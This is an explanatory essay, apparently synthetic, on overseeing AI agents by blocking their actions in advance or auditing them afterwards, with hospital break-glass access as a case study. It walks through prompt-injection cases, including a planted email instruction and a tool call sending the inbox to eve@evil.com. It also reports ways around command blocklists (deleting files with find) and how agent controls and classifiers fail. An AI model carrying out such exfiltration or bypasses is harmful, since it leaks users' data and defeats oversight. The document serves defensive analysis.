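# Blocking AI agent actions in advance or auditing them afterwards

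## Two ways to oversee what an AI agent does

An AI agent is a system in which an AI model chooses its own steps towards a goal and carries them out through other software. Companies use agents to write and run code, sort email and handle expense claims. These actions change files, accounts and messages that people depend on, so somebody has to oversee them, through either preventive blocking or after-the-fact audits. Preventive blocking is any control that can stop an action before it runs. An after-the-fact audit lets actions run and records them for somebody to review later. Hospitals have faced a version of this choice for decades.

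### What one agent action looks like

*Trustworthy agents in practice*, from the AI company Anthropic, describes an agent's work as a loop in which the agent plans, acts, observes the result, adjusts, and repeats until it has finished or needs a person. Suppose an employee asks an agent to submit photos of receipts from a business trip. The agent transcribes each photo, picks out the amount and the vendor, chooses a category, and files the claim through the company's system. If the system flags a hotel bill for exceeding the nightly cap, the agent may stop and ask whether it should look up the expense policy before trying again.

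An AI agent differs from a chatbot in having tools, which are pieces of software that the model can call. A chatbot can draft an email, but sending it requires a tool. An agent action, or tool call, is one step by which an agent affects a system outside itself, such as running a command, editing a file or sending a message. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) defines an agent as an AI system with tools that allow it to take actions, and uses the single tool call as its unit of analysis.

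When an AI agent uses a tool, the model produces a structured request containing the tool's name and the details to pass to it. Ordinary software around the model, often called the harness, reads the request, runs the operation and returns the result to the model, which then produces its next request. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, "the model never runs anything on its own." A control can therefore block an action after the model requests it and before the software runs it. Whoever runs the tool controls whether this check happens. Anthropic's own servers run web search and a few other tools, and a customer's software usually receives those requests together with their results, too late to block the action.

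### One deletion, from request to review

Anthropic keeps an internal log of incidents in which its agents did something they should not have. The company's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes several, all involving its coding agent, Claude Code. In one, a user asked the agent to "clean up old branches." The agent listed the branches on the shared server, wrote a pattern to match some of them, and issued a command to delete the matches.

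A branch is a named line of work in Git, the system most programming teams use to track their code. The same branch can exist on a programmer's own machine and on a server the whole team uses. The user may have wanted to tidy up only their own machine, in which case the agent was about to delete other people's work.

Anthropic lists four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action: it is overeager and goes beyond what the user would approve; it makes an honest mistake about what its action will affect; an attacker has planted instructions in a file or web page it reads (a prompt injection); or the model is misaligned and pursues its own goal. The branch deletion looks like overeagerness, perhaps combined with a mistake.

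The earliest control that could act here is a fixed rule. Users of Claude Code can write a rule that denies a particular command, and Anthropic applies deny rules in every mode. A team can also put a rule on the server. On GitHub, a service that hosts shared code, a team can protect all branches whose names fit a pattern, such as every name that contains "release". GitHub's *About protected branches* explains that protected branches can't be deleted by default. The server would then refuse to delete the protected branches and carry out the rest of the agent's command. Administrators are exempt unless the team decides otherwise, so an agent using an administrator's credentials would normally be exempt too. This kind of rule is based on the branch's name and the type of operation, not on what the user meant by "clean up".

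A permission prompt lets a person approve or refuse one action before it runs. When an agent is about to delete branches on a server, for example, only the user knows which ones they wanted to delete. If they read the command and refuse it, the server is unchanged and the agent can try something narrower. Reading the command may take some care, because an agent that deletes by pattern may show the pattern and not the branches it matches, and then the user has to work out the list or ask for it.

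An automatic check replaces the person with an AI classifier, a second model that allows or blocks each action. Anthropic writes that its classifier is designed to block this deletion because the request was vague, the action was irreversible and destructive, and the user may have meant only local branches. After a denial, the agent can look for a safer route, such as deleting the local branches or asking the user what they meant. Unlike a person, the classifier does not become less attentive through boredom, but it has to infer the user's intention from the conversation, so it has less information than the user.

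Once an agent has deleted branches from a server, a reviewer has only the log to work with. The log can't restore the branches, but a good entry can make the repair much easier. For example, the command `git ls-remote` lists the branches on a server with the identifier of each one's latest commit. If the agent happened to run that command before the deletion and the log kept the output, a reviewer has the information needed to recreate every branch under its old name.

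How much a reviewer can still change depends on when the review takes place. Anthropic's word "irreversible" is too strong for the first days after a branch is deleted. *Remote Branches*, a chapter of the handbook on Git's website, explains that deleting a branch on a server removes only the pointer. The server generally keeps the data until a clean-up process called garbage collection runs, so recovery is often easy before then. Git's *Maintenance and Data Recovery* gives the steps for finding the lost commit and creating a new branch that points to it. GitHub also has a button for restoring some branches. Its *Deleting and restoring branches in a pull request* covers branches that belonged to a closed pull request (a proposal to merge the branch that is no longer open).

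The time limit leaves less room for recovery than it suggests. Git keeps unreferenced data for two weeks by default, while the handbook refers to data that is "a few months old", and whoever runs the server can set the period to zero. Both figures refer to the age of the data, so older branches may be among the first to disappear. Even when the work is recovered, a colleague has still lost the afternoon they spent looking for it.

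Some reviews happen so quickly that the difference between blocking an action and auditing it afterwards matters little in practice. OpenAI, the maker of ChatGPT, runs an automated review of its internal coding agents after each session ends. IT Brief UK reports that the system reviews interactions within 30 minutes of completion and sends suspicious cases to people. A deletion in the first minute of a three-hour session could still wait more than three hours for review.

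### Two kinds of error, and what a late catch is worth

Every method of oversight can make two kinds of error. A preventive control can let a harmful action through (a miss) or stop a legitimate one (a false block). An audit can fail to flag a harmful action, which is also a miss, or flag a legitimate one (a false flag). The miss rate, which engineers usually call the false-negative rate, is the share of harmful actions that a method lets through or fails to flag. The false-positive rate is the share of legitimate actions that it stops or flags.

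One small false block also involved deleting a branch. In *Git repos and protected branches*, Shipilev (2020) told a mailing list for Java developers that the server would not let him delete a branch he had used to run tests and no longer needed. The error message was "Cannot delete this protected branch," and he wondered whether somebody had changed the settings. The only consequence was his puzzled email. If the server had instead allowed the deletion and wrongly flagged it for review, the branch would have been gone as he wished, and a reviewer would have spent a few minutes finding out that nothing was wrong.

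The two errors can be hard to tell apart because the same command may be authorised in one case and not in another. If the user who asked for a clean-up meant to include the branches on the server, the agent's deletion was legitimate and stopping it would have been a false block. Anyone measuring a miss rate therefore has to decide first what the user authorised, and two careful people may disagree.

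The base rate, which is the share of all actions that are harmful, strongly affects what proportion of blocks or flags are mistaken. In a hypothetical example, an agent performs 10,000 actions, of which 10 are harmful. A control with a 20% miss rate stops 8 of them. If it also wrongly stops 1% of the 9,990 legitimate actions, it produces about 100 false blocks, so roughly 13 of every 14 blocks are mistaken. An audit with the same error rates would flag about 108 actions for review, of which only 8 were harmful. False blocks delay the user's task, while false flags take up reviewers' time.

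Two further quantities apply only to audits. The review delay is the time between an action and when someone able to respond learns that it was wrong, so an unread alert does not end the delay. The recoverable share is the part of an action's harm that people can still undo when a review catches the action. For the deleted branches, this share starts high and falls as the clean-up approaches. For a password that an agent has posted on a public website, it may be low from the first minute, because the owner can change the password but cannot undo anything a stranger has already done with it.

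These definitions allow a rough comparison if we assume that all harmful actions do equal damage. A block with miss rate *b* prevents a share of the harm equal to 1 − *b*. An audit with miss rate *a* undoes a share equal to (1 − *a*) × *r*, where *r* is the recoverable share. Suppose a poor block misses 40% of harmful actions and an excellent audit misses 5%. If people can undo half of the harm, blocking prevents 60% of it and the audit repairs 47.5%, so the block does better. If they can undo nine-tenths, the audit repairs 85.5%, well above the block's 60%.

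An audit may also prevent some harmful actions if those who expect a review behave better. Let *d* be the share of harmful actions prevented this way. The audit's total becomes *d* + (1 − *d*) × (1 − *a*) × *r*. If *d* is 30% and half of the harm is recoverable, the total is about 63%, which is now slightly better than the poor block. The formula leaves out the cost of running either method, and whether *d* is close to 30%, or even above zero, is an empirical question.

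### Three positions and five questions

The first position is to block any action with serious consequences until a fixed rule or a person has allowed it. Its supporters argue that some damage cannot be repaired, and that a mistake is easiest to deal with before it happens.

Others would let the agent act and log what it does, then have people review the log and fix any mistakes. They argue that most actions are harmless and most mistakes can be repaired, so asking permission each time wastes effort and tires the people who have to answer.

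A third group would let a classifier stop risky actions and allow the rest without asking anyone. They accept that the classifier will miss some harmful actions, because they expect tired reviewers to miss more.

Commercial products already draw on all three. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) describes five commercial agents as relying mostly on frequent prompts or on review by another AI model. Claude Code used to ask by default, but Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announced in August that an automatic check by another model would take over for new sessions on most subscription plans. The company still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. Cursor, another coding tool, covers many commands with lists of permitted actions and with sandboxing (running code in a closed-off space), and uses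 a classifier for much of the rest. OpenAI's internal review happens after the agent has acted. An organisation can combine these methods, so the dispute is mostly about which should handle ordinary cases.

The three positions part on five questions:

- How much misuse does each method catch, counting every harmful action whatever its cause?
- Does the prospect of an audit change behaviour, or does it only help with cleaning up?
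- How much reviewer time does each method need, whether the reviewer answers prompts or reads logs?
- What do wrongly blocked actions cost, in lost work and in people who switch the control off?
- Which harms can wait for a review, and for how long?

Hospitals are a useful comparison because they have had to weigh the same errors with more at stake. Restricting access to a patient's record protects privacy, but it can also keep a doctor from information that the patient urgently needs. Hospitals therefore use break-glass access, which lets staff override a restriction by giving a reason and logs the access for review. The American Medical Association's *Are "Break-the-Glass" functions required for employee EHR access?* (an EHR is an electronic health record) describes a version in which the user has to authenticate again and document a specific business reason before the chart opens. Hospitals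 have years of experience with logs, reviewers and staff who know that somebody may check. The comparison is weakest on deterrence, because the risk of losing a job can discourage a nurse from prying into a neighbour's record but doesn't apply to an AI agent.

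## What hospitals learned from break-glass access to patient records

Break-glass access is named after breaking the glass to pull a fire alarm, as *Misuse of 'Break-the-Glass' Policies in Hospitals* explains. *A Portable, Patient-Possessed Health Record* (2026) proposes a health card that patients carry, with a break-glass option for emergencies in which the patient is unconscious and can't approve access.

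### From a closed record to a log entry

Most record systems use role-based access control. An administrator assigns permissions to roles such as "ward nurse" or "surgeon", and each employee gets the permissions of the roles they hold. A nurse may, for example, have access only to the records of patients on one ward.

Hospital work doesn't fit these roles. Patients move between departments, and a doctor on one ward asks a doctor on another for advice. Røstad's doctoral thesis, *Access Control in Healthcare Information Systems* (2009), describes care as often unpredictable and hard to fit into strict rules, so clinicians sometimes need a way to bypass them.

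*Log Analysis of Human Computer Interactions Regarding Break The Glass Accesses* (Ferreira, Farinha and colleagues, 2013) describes how the São João hospital in Porto, the second largest in Portugal, controls access to genetic reports. Portuguese law reserves these reports for staff whose speciality directly concerns genetics. When a doctor outside the authorised group tries to open one, the system instead shows a warning that explains the override, the law behind the restriction and the possible consequences of going on. The doctor can then give up, or open the report by picking one of two ready-made reasons or typing their own.

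In break-glass access, the clinician who wants the record also answers the prompt, so nobody else approves the request. Norwegian sources call this self-authorisation. A coding agent's permission prompt, by contrast, goes to a person who can refuse the action.

The system then writes a log entry. Under Stanford University's *HIPAA Security* policy on audit controls, an entry should record at least the type of event and its result, the date and time, the user's ID, and the program or command that started the event. The system can also alert a responsible person by email, text message or phone, who then checks whether the access was justified. Some hospitals limit what the override opens. *Tilgangsstyring av elektronisk pasientjournal* (Hystad, 2014), a Norwegian master's thesis on access to patient records, mentions systems in which emergency users must re-enter their password, repeat the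 override for each part of the record, and lose access after a set time.

The security rule under HIPAA, the US health privacy law, requires hospitals to have a procedure for obtaining patient information in an emergency (45 CFR 164.312). According to Network Computing's summary, the same section also requires them to record and examine activity in systems that hold electronic patient data. US law doesn't prescribe break-glass access as the way to meet these requirements. Another part of the rule requires hospitals to review their audit logs regularly, but each hospital decides how many entries someone has to read.

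Some American hospitals put break-glass on the records of all their employees and the employees' families, since colleagues are most likely to be curious. The AMA points out that HIPAA doesn't require this. It would rather have hospitals restrict records only for employees who ask, because every extra validation step takes clinicians' time away from patients. It sees a use for break-glass when outside users, such as another hospital's emergency department, open sensitive records.

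### An exception that Norwegian staff used every day

Norwegian hospitals have two kinds of override, according to *Styring og kontroll av tilgang til helseopplysninger i elektroniske pasientjournaler*, by the national audit office, Riksrevisjonen. A routine override, called *aktualisering* in Norwegian, opens the record of a patient who is on another ward, has gone home or has not yet arrived. Emergency access opens the record of any patient, whether in general medicine, psychiatry or addiction treatment. Both require a reason and leave a log entry.

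Røstad and Edsberg (2006), in *A Study of Access Control Requirements for Healthcare Systems*, examined the access logs of a hospital record system that relied heavily on overrides. Staff used overrides so often, and in so many parts of the hospital, that the researchers no longer considered them exceptions. They also judged that auditing the log for misuse was not feasible, because it was huge and the reasons recorded in it were either ready-made or uninformative.

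Hystad gives numbers from Røstad's later thesis, which covered eight hospitals in Central Norway. In one month, staff used the routine override 54,096 times and emergency access 67 times. If each entry took two minutes to review, one person could review the emergency accesses in an afternoon, but the routine overrides would take about 1,800 hours, or a month's work for eleven people.

Hystad also gives the routine override as 17% of all record openings and emergency access as 0.07%. These can't be shares of the same total, because 54,096 routine overrides at 17% implies about 318,000 openings, while 67 emergency accesses at 0.07% implies about 96,000. The counts are therefore safer to compare than the percentages.

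An internal project at Rikshospitalet, a large hospital in Oslo, found a similar share. According to Hystad, staff there used the routine override for about 15% of the documents they opened. A third of its most frequent users did not consciously choose a reason. In interviews with 17 heavy users, about half found the override irritating and half said that one gets used to it.

The ready-made reasons help explain why a reviewer would learn so little from these logs. One widely used Norwegian system offers up to fifteen, including research, teaching, internal quality control and an enquiry from the patient's relatives. An employee who wants to look up a neighbour can choose "teaching" as easily as a lecturer can. To tell them apart, a reviewer would have to ask the employee or check a timetable for each of thousands of entries. *Access Control in Heterogenous Health Care Systems*, a Norwegian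 simulation study, agreed with Røstad and Edsberg about a complete audit at a large hospital, and found that checking even a few percent of the entries would be a very large job.

Riksrevisjonen tested four of Norway's largest hospital trusts in the spring of 2014, eight years after Røstad and Edsberg's paper. All four had written procedures for routine log checks, but none carried out systematic checks on its own initiative. The few checks they made were mostly at patients' request. Their record systems accepted any word, or a single character, as a reason for an override. In two of the trusts, staff had lent each other their logins, so the logs recorded the wrong person. At the University Hospital of North Norway, one employee's override also opened the record to other staff for 24 hours. Riksrevisjonen concluded that it would be almost a matter of chance whether the trusts discovered snooping.

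The health ministry itself held that broad access requires good logging and a working system of checks. The trusts had broad access and logs, but hardly anybody checked the logs. The Norwegian experience is therefore poor evidence about how well auditing works, but better evidence that an organisation can promise an audit, build the log and never read it.

Convenience also led to wider permissions. In 2012, Sørlandet Hospital introduced a newer system that ties access to decisions about a patient's treatment, such as a referral. Staff complained that they still had to use overrides too often, so the hospital granted broader normal access than it had first wanted. This reduces the number of logged overrides but doesn't show that anyone's access has become more appropriate. *Deficiencies in how healthcare providers control staff access to patient journal data* describes a similar problem with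 normal access in Sweden, where the Swedish Authority for Privacy Protection audited eight care providers and found that seven did not limit staff to what their tasks strictly required.

### Genetic reports in Porto

Until May 2009, São João hospital's system logged staff outside the authorised group when they opened genetic reports but did nothing to stop them. The hospital then switched on the warning window, and Ferreira and colleagues compared the logs from before and after the change.

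| | November 2007 to April 2009 | May 2009 to December 2012 |
|---|---|---|
| Length | 18 months | 44 months |
| Genetic reports in the system | 2,875 | 7,774 |
| Openings by authorised staff | 159 | 567 |
| Attempts by other staff | 842 | 5,608 |
| Attempts they completed | 842 | 3,071 |
| Attempts they abandoned | none | 2,537 |

After the change, staff outside the group gave up on 45% of their attempts to open genetic reports. The number of reports they opened still rose, from about 47 a month to about 70, but by then the hospital held far more of them. Relative to the number of reports held, staff seem to have tried as often as before, making about 16 attempts a month per thousand reports in both periods. This calculation is crude because it uses one total for each period while the collection was growing.

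Some of the 2,537 abandoned attempts will have been snooping that the warning prevented, but others were probably made by doctors who needed the report and got it a minute later. The three people who used the override most also abandoned many attempts. One of them gave up 128 times and went ahead 131 times, always giving the reason that they belonged, or should belong, to the authorised group. Ferreira and colleagues suspect that some users close the window, try again, and accept the override once they see no other way to the report. In 93% of the abandoned attempts, the user closed the browser instead of pressing the button for "I don't want to see this report". They may have mistaken the warning for an error, or hoped that closing the window would leave no trace.

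The reasons are more informative than the Norwegian ones, at least where staff wrote their own. Of the 3,071 completed overrides, 40% cited urgency and 27% cited membership of the authorised group. In the remaining third, users typed a reason, and just over half of them said they were the patient's doctor and had requested the test. A doctor reading the result of a test they ordered seems unlikely to be misuse, so the fault is more likely in the list of authorised staff, or in the law behind it. Staff outside the list made nine out of ten attempts to open these reports.

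The ready-made reasons have the same weakness as in Norway. One user chose "urgent" for 134 of 137 overrides, which looks more like a habit of clicking the same line, although a genetic result can be urgent. In six cases the system accepted an empty answer. During 2012 the number of typed reasons fell by almost 60%, and Ferreira and colleagues could not tell whether staff had become more careful or had found the information elsewhere, for example on paper.

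They also ask whether anybody at the hospital was reviewing the overrides and, if so, who did it, when and how. The drop in completed attempts therefore can't count as evidence for after-the-fact audits. It came from a warning that staff saw before they opened the report, which is closer to a preventive control, though users can always overrule it. *Effectiveness of Email Warning on Reducing Hospital Employees' Unauthorized Access* reports a trial at an American medical centre that tested the effect of warning staff after the access.

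Both sets of usage figures are old. The Norwegian logs date from 2009 or earlier, and the Porto data end in 2012. Record systems have changed since then, and current rates of use could be higher or lower. In *Artificial Intelligence–Based Framework for Analyzing Health Care Staff Security Practice*, Yeng, Nweke and colleagues (2021) studied software that could find misuse in access logs, but they tested it on simulated data.

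### Why hospitals rely on audits for a harm they can't undo

Hospitals allow break-glass access even though a later review can't undo a breach of privacy. A hospital can dismiss an employee who has read a neighbour's diagnosis, but the employee still knows the diagnosis. The recoverable share is therefore close to zero, and the formula in the previous section would strongly favour blocking.

They do so because stopping legitimate actions also causes harm, which the formula ignores. It counts only the harm from actions that should not have happened. In a hypothetical set of 1,000 attempts to override a restriction, 10 come from curiosity and 990 from staff who need the record. A system that refuses all of them prevents 10 intrusions and delays 990 pieces of work. Most of those delays will mean only that somebody has to make a phone call, but if one involves an unconscious patient with a dangerous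 allergy, the refusal could kill the patient.

The comparison can be put as an inequality. Let *p* be the share of override attempts that are improper, *D* the average harm of an improper reading, and *W* the average harm of a wrong refusal. Refusing everyone does less damage than admitting everyone only if

*p* × *D* > (1 − *p*) × *W*.

If 1% of attempts are improper (*p*), blocking is justified only if an improper reading does more than 99 times as much harm (*D*) as the average wrong refusal (*W*). If half are improper, the reading only has to do more harm than the refusal. *D* is higher when a disclosure can't be undone, but a large *W* or a small *p* can outweigh that.

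Hystad reports that Røstad's thesis draws the same contrast between health care and other systems on which safety depends. The standard rule for railway signals, nuclear plants and banks is to deny access in case of doubt, whereas the rule in health care is to allow it.

The size of *W* is uncertain. Yeng and colleagues warn that wrongly refusing access may worsen a patient's condition and even lead to death, but they don't count cases. Hystad cites a Norwegian survey of 395 doctors, medical secretaries and radiographers, in which 26.5% said that missing access had kept them from carrying out tasks. That is a large share, but the survey doesn't show how often patients were harmed. Privacy also matters for safety, because patients who don't trust the hospital may hold back information that their doctors need. In 2008, the European Court of Human Rights ruled against Finland over a hospital's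 failure to protect a patient's record.

When the recoverable share is zero, the formula for an audit's value reduces to *d*, the share of misuse that never happens because staff expect a review. A review can also stop somebody from repeating the misuse, but otherwise audits protect privacy only through deterrence, which requires staff to believe that somebody reads the log. In 2008 the Norwegian health inspectorate listed the low risk of discovery and punishment among the causes of poor access control.

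Logging can also discourage staff from reading records they need. In the same survey of 395 staff, 5.1% said they had at least once not read information they should have read, because the log could trace the access to them. In a later survey of 264 staff at Oslo University Hospital, 14.7% agreed at least slightly that the thought of the log had stopped them from reading something they professionally ought to have read. Counts of refused requests miss these false blocks because the system never refused anything.

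### Where an AI agent differs from a clinician

For most agent actions, *W* is much smaller. If a control wrongly stops a coding agent from deleting old branches, the agent can ask the user or do something else, and the branches stay for another hour. The hospitals' main reason for letting people through is therefore absent from a lot of ordinary agent work. It does apply when delay causes damage. An agent trying to isolate a computer during an attack, or restore a failed payment system, is in a position more like the emergency doctor's, and a refusal at the wrong moment could do more harm than most of the agent's mistakes.

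An agent has no job or licence to lose, so a value of *d* measured on nurses doesn't apply to it. The people around the agent can still respond to incentives, and an employee who starts one may give it narrower permissions if they expect to answer for what it does. For that, the log has to show who started the agent, what they asked for and which account it used. Norwegian hospitals lost the link between account and person when staff lent each other their logins. An organisation could lose it every day if its agents run under their users' own accounts.

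Clinicians are also few in number and open records slowly. On an average day at São João, about 450 professionals opened some 1,500 reports in the shared record system, or three to four each. A curious employee might look at a dozen records before anybody noticed. A hundred copies of an agent, each opening one report a second, would open all of the roughly three million reports available in the system in a little over eight hours. A review the next morning would limit the damage from the employee but would come too late for the agent. A hospital that gave an agent break-glass access would need to cap the number of records the agent could open before a person looked at the log.

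Break-glass access mostly concerns reading, and when the reader is a person, the harm is done once they have seen the page. An agent that reads a confidential file has passed its text to whoever runs the model, which may or may not matter, but it would have to take another action to tell a colleague or post the text online, and a control can block that action. In this respect an agent's reading is easier to contain than a person's. But agents also delete files, send payments and change settings, and two decades of experience with who looked at which record offer little guidance on those actions.

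The reason field would probably be less useful for agents as well. A clinician who types a false reason is lying under their own name, and the Porto figures suggest that some people turn back at that point. A language model can write a plausible reason for any action in a second or two. If an attacker has planted instructions in something the agent read, the attacker may have supplied the reason. Self-authorisation makes sense for doctors because the hospital already trusts their judgement of what the patient needs. The control on an agent is there to check the agent's judgement, so letting the agent authorise itself means relying on the same judgement that was supposed to be checked.

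### What carries over

The contrast between 67 emergency accesses and 54,096 routine ones applies to agents with little change. An organisation that wants people to review every case in which an agent overrides a restriction has to set the restriction so that this happens only a few times a day, and handle the rest another way. Otherwise it will have too many overrides to review, as in the log that Røstad and Edsberg gave up on.

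The hospital logs can help in deciding what to do with the rest. Røstad and Edsberg found that the informative reasons were a good starting point for working out which needs the normal rules should have covered. At São João, the obvious candidate for normal access was the doctor who had ordered the test. In a team that uses coding agents, it might be a command that people have approved two hundred times and never refused. Moving such cases into the normal permissions makes overrides rare again, so a reviewer can give the remaining ones some attention. The risk is that permissions grow because people are tired of the prompt, as happened at Sørlandet Hospital. Somebody should look at what the approved cases have in common before making them automatic.

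A stated reason is most useful when a reviewer can check it against something the requester did not write. For a doctor, this could be a referral or an appointment, and the newer Norwegian systems grant access on that basis. For an agent, it could be the user's original request or an open repair ticket. If the agent claims it deleted a database because the user asked it to, software can at least check whether the user mentioned a database.

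Finally, hospitals have found that patients can review access to their own records at almost no cost to the hospital. Norwegian patients can log in to Helsenorge's *Patient records* service and see which hospital employees have opened their record. A patient may recognise the name of a former husband or a neighbour, which would mean nothing to a security officer with a list of a million openings. An organisation could likewise notify the owner of a file or branch whenever an agent changes it, since the owner knows whether the change was wanted. But owners have to read the notifications, and they would soon stop if an agent made hundreds of changes a day.

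## The case for blocking before the action

### Refusal by default

The usual practice in computer security is to refuse access in case of doubt, whereas hospitals let clinicians through. The field had settled on two rules for this by 1975. Least privilege means every program and user holds only the permissions the job requires. Refusal by default means a system starts from no access and sets conditions for granting it, instead of granting everything and listing exceptions. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) applies least privilege to agents together with a third old rule, complete mediation, which requires a check on every protected operation and not only the first.

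The argument for refusal by default is that people notice its mistakes. Suppose an administrator forgets a case when writing the rules. If the rules list what is permitted, the system refuses the forgotten action, somebody complains about the false block the same day, and it gets repaired. If the rules list what is forbidden, the system allows the forgotten action, and the miss may last for years because nobody complains about being allowed to do too much.

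Computer scientists of the 1970s also considered recording break-ins instead of preventing them, but thought this rarely suited computers. An intruder who has taken over a computer can often erase the traces, whereas a burglar who forces a locked filing cabinet leaves it broken. An AI agent with an administrator's permissions could likewise erase the log of its own actions.

### A nurse's record in Finland

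In 1996, a Finnish nurse could not find out which hospital employees had opened her patient record, which Norwegian patients can now look up. In *I v. Finland* (2008), the European Court of Human Rights had to decide whether Finland had failed to protect her privacy.

She had worked in the eye clinic of a public hospital, and another clinic there treated her for HIV. All staff could open the patient register, including diagnoses. Early in 1992 she began to suspect that her colleagues knew about her illness. She told her doctor that summer, and the hospital then allowed only the clinic that treated her to open her record and registered her under a false name.

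Four years later she asked the county authorities to find out who had read her record. The head of the hospital's archive replied that the system showed only the five most recent consultations, listed them by department rather than by person, and deleted them once the file went back to the archive. She sued, and the Finnish appeal court believed her account of her colleagues' hints and remarks, but it found no firm evidence that anybody had opened the record unlawfully and ordered her to pay the other side's costs.

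Before the European court, the Finnish government argued that no hospital could verify every request in advance, because staff often need records immediately, and that she had been free to claim damages. The judges unanimously found that Finland had violated her right to private life. They held that a chance of compensation was not enough, because the state owed her safeguards that worked in practice and would "exclude any possibility of unauthorised access occurring in the first place". They awarded her about €13,800 in damages, plus her legal costs.

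The judgment as a whole supports blocking less strongly than that sentence suggests. The judges also wrote that the nurse would have been in a better position if the hospital had either restricted access to the people treating her or kept a log of everyone who opened the file. The decisive point for them was that the register broke Finnish data protection law. The hospital introduced a complete log in 1998, but the court did not have to rule on whether such a log would have been enough by itself.

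The case is stronger evidence about who bears the burden when prevention fails. The hospital had kept poor records, yet the Finnish courts expected the nurse to prove what had happened. As for urgency, the hospital had shown in 1992 that it could restrict a record to one clinic without checking each request.

### Sandboxes and lists of commands

The simplest way to block an agent's actions is to put the agent in a sandbox with no outside network access. The agent can still damage the files inside, but it can't email them to anyone, however badly it misunderstands its task. This works without anyone having to recognise a harmful action.

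Most useful agents need some outside connection, though, and each connection brings back part of the risk. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) gives the example of a sandbox that permits outgoing email. An attacker can then plant an instruction that makes the agent send confidential data in an ordinary-looking message. The sandbox controls whether the agent may send email, but not which data it may send to whom.

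Lists of forbidden commands give finer control. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026), a survey of 39 papers, reports a test of 1,709 such lists collected from GitHub. A program called ShellSieve used a language model to propose ways around each list, then ran them in a sandbox to see which worked. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists proved fragile, depending on the type of workaround. For example, a list that forbids `rm`, the usual command for deleting files, doesn't stop an agent from deleting them with `find`.

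A list of permitted commands follows the rule of refusal by default, so nobody has to think of every synonym for a forbidden command. But if the list permits Python, the agent can write a Python program that deletes the files. A safer list has to limit the details of each command as well as its name.

### One policy and one call

Progent, a system by Shi, He and colleagues (2025), sits between an agent and its tools. It compares every call with a policy, which is a list of rules about tool names and the values passed to them.

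In their worked example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice with the subject "TODOs for the week". The email asks for a summary of the user's recent emails, posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace messaging service. By the time the agent has found the email, looked up the Slack name and read the inbox, the policy allows four kinds of call:

- `search_emails`, for that sender and that subject
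- `get_slack_info`
- `read_emails`, for the 20 most recent messages
- `send_slack_msg`, if the recipient is `alice`, the user's own Slack name

One of the 20 messages contains an attacker's instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com. The agent follows it and requests `send_email(to=eve@evil.com, body=<inbox>)`.

Progent first collects the rules for `send_email`. Rules that forbid a call take priority over rules that allow it, but this policy has neither for email. Progent blocks any call that matches no rule, so the email is never sent. The agent receives an error message with instructions to try something else and continue with the user's task. It next requests `send_slack_msg(to=alice, body=<summary>)`, which matches the Slack rule and runs. A Slack message to anyone else would have failed because the rule allows only Alice as the recipient.

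Nobody could have written this policy before the task began, since only Alice's email revealed that the agent would need Slack. Progent therefore has a language model write a first policy from the user's request and propose changes as the agent learns more. If *A*(*P*) is the set of calls that policy *P* allows, a new policy *P*′ takes effect automatically only if

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*),

that is, if it allows nothing that the old one didn't. A solver, a program that settles such logical questions exactly, does the comparison. Any change that adds a permission needs approval, from a person or from a setting chosen in advance. An attacker who fools the policy-writing model can make it ask for `send_email`, but cannot make it grant the permission silently.

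Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated banking, travel, messaging and office tasks in which attackers plant instructions in the data that an agent reads. The agent and the policy writer both ran on GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. Progent reduced the attack success rate, the share of attempts in which the agent does what the attacker wanted, from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many tasks as it did without Progent. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools.

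These tests automatically approved every request for more permissions, to imitate a careless user, so the solver's safeguard did not produce the 1.0%. Attack success on AgentDojo was 2.5% when the first policy was frozen for the whole task, and zero when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion. Only 6% of policy changes were expansions, so this reviewer would have had far less to read than someone approving each action.

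### Following the data

An agent is at risk when the model that decides what to do also reads text from strangers, so CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, divides the work between two models. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes the procedure. A privileged model sees only the user's request and writes a short Python program that fixes which tools will run, in what order and under what conditions. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the emails and web pages and extracts what the program needs. An instruction hidden in an email therefore reaches only a model that can't act on it. Outside text can affect which branch of the program runs, but it can't add a step.

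An attacker might still tamper with the data. Suppose a user asks the agent to find some meeting notes and send a summary to the colleague named in them. The plan is sound, but anyone who can edit the notes can change the colleague's address. CaMeL therefore labels every value. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), the labels record where the value came from and who may read it, and a policy checks them before each tool call and returns "allow" or "deny". If the notes are confidential and the address belongs to somebody outside the company, the policy can deny the call.

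*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarises the first results as eliminating nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. Later tests confirm the reduction in attacks, but their results on task performance are less favourable. In *CapLite*, Xu, Liu and Nakayama (2026) reran CaMeL and Progent on 15 freely downloadable models, 13 of them small (up to 12 billion parameters). They also tested their own design, CapLite, in which the model writes no policy. Ordinary code works out from the tool descriptions which calls change something. The model must commit to its list of such calls before it reads any outside data, and the code refuses a call if its recipient, amount or target doesn't appear in the user's request.

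| Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks out of 13,935 |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 59.4% | 50.2% | 2,322 (16.7%) |
| Progent | 43.8% | 40.6% | 676 (4.9%) |
| CaMeL | 24.9% | 27.2% | 20 (0.1%) |
| CapLite | 28.1% | 29.0% | 0 |

On undefended agents, 2,322 attacks worked, compared with 676 on agents defended by Progent and 20 on agents defended by CaMeL. Dividing by the undefended total gives a miss rate of about 29% for Progent and just under 1% for CaMeL. The same calculation for Progent's original test with GPT-4o gives about 2.5%. These rates are approximate because some attacks that got past a defence may have failed on undefended agents.

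Progent did worse here because small models wrote its policies, which let attacks through and also blocked calls that the task needed. Within the Qwen3 family, attack success under Progent rose from 3.0% for the smallest model to 14.2% for the largest, because the larger models followed planted instructions more readily and their policies did not make up for it. The largest had 32 billion parameters, far fewer than the leading models of 2026, so the trend may not continue.

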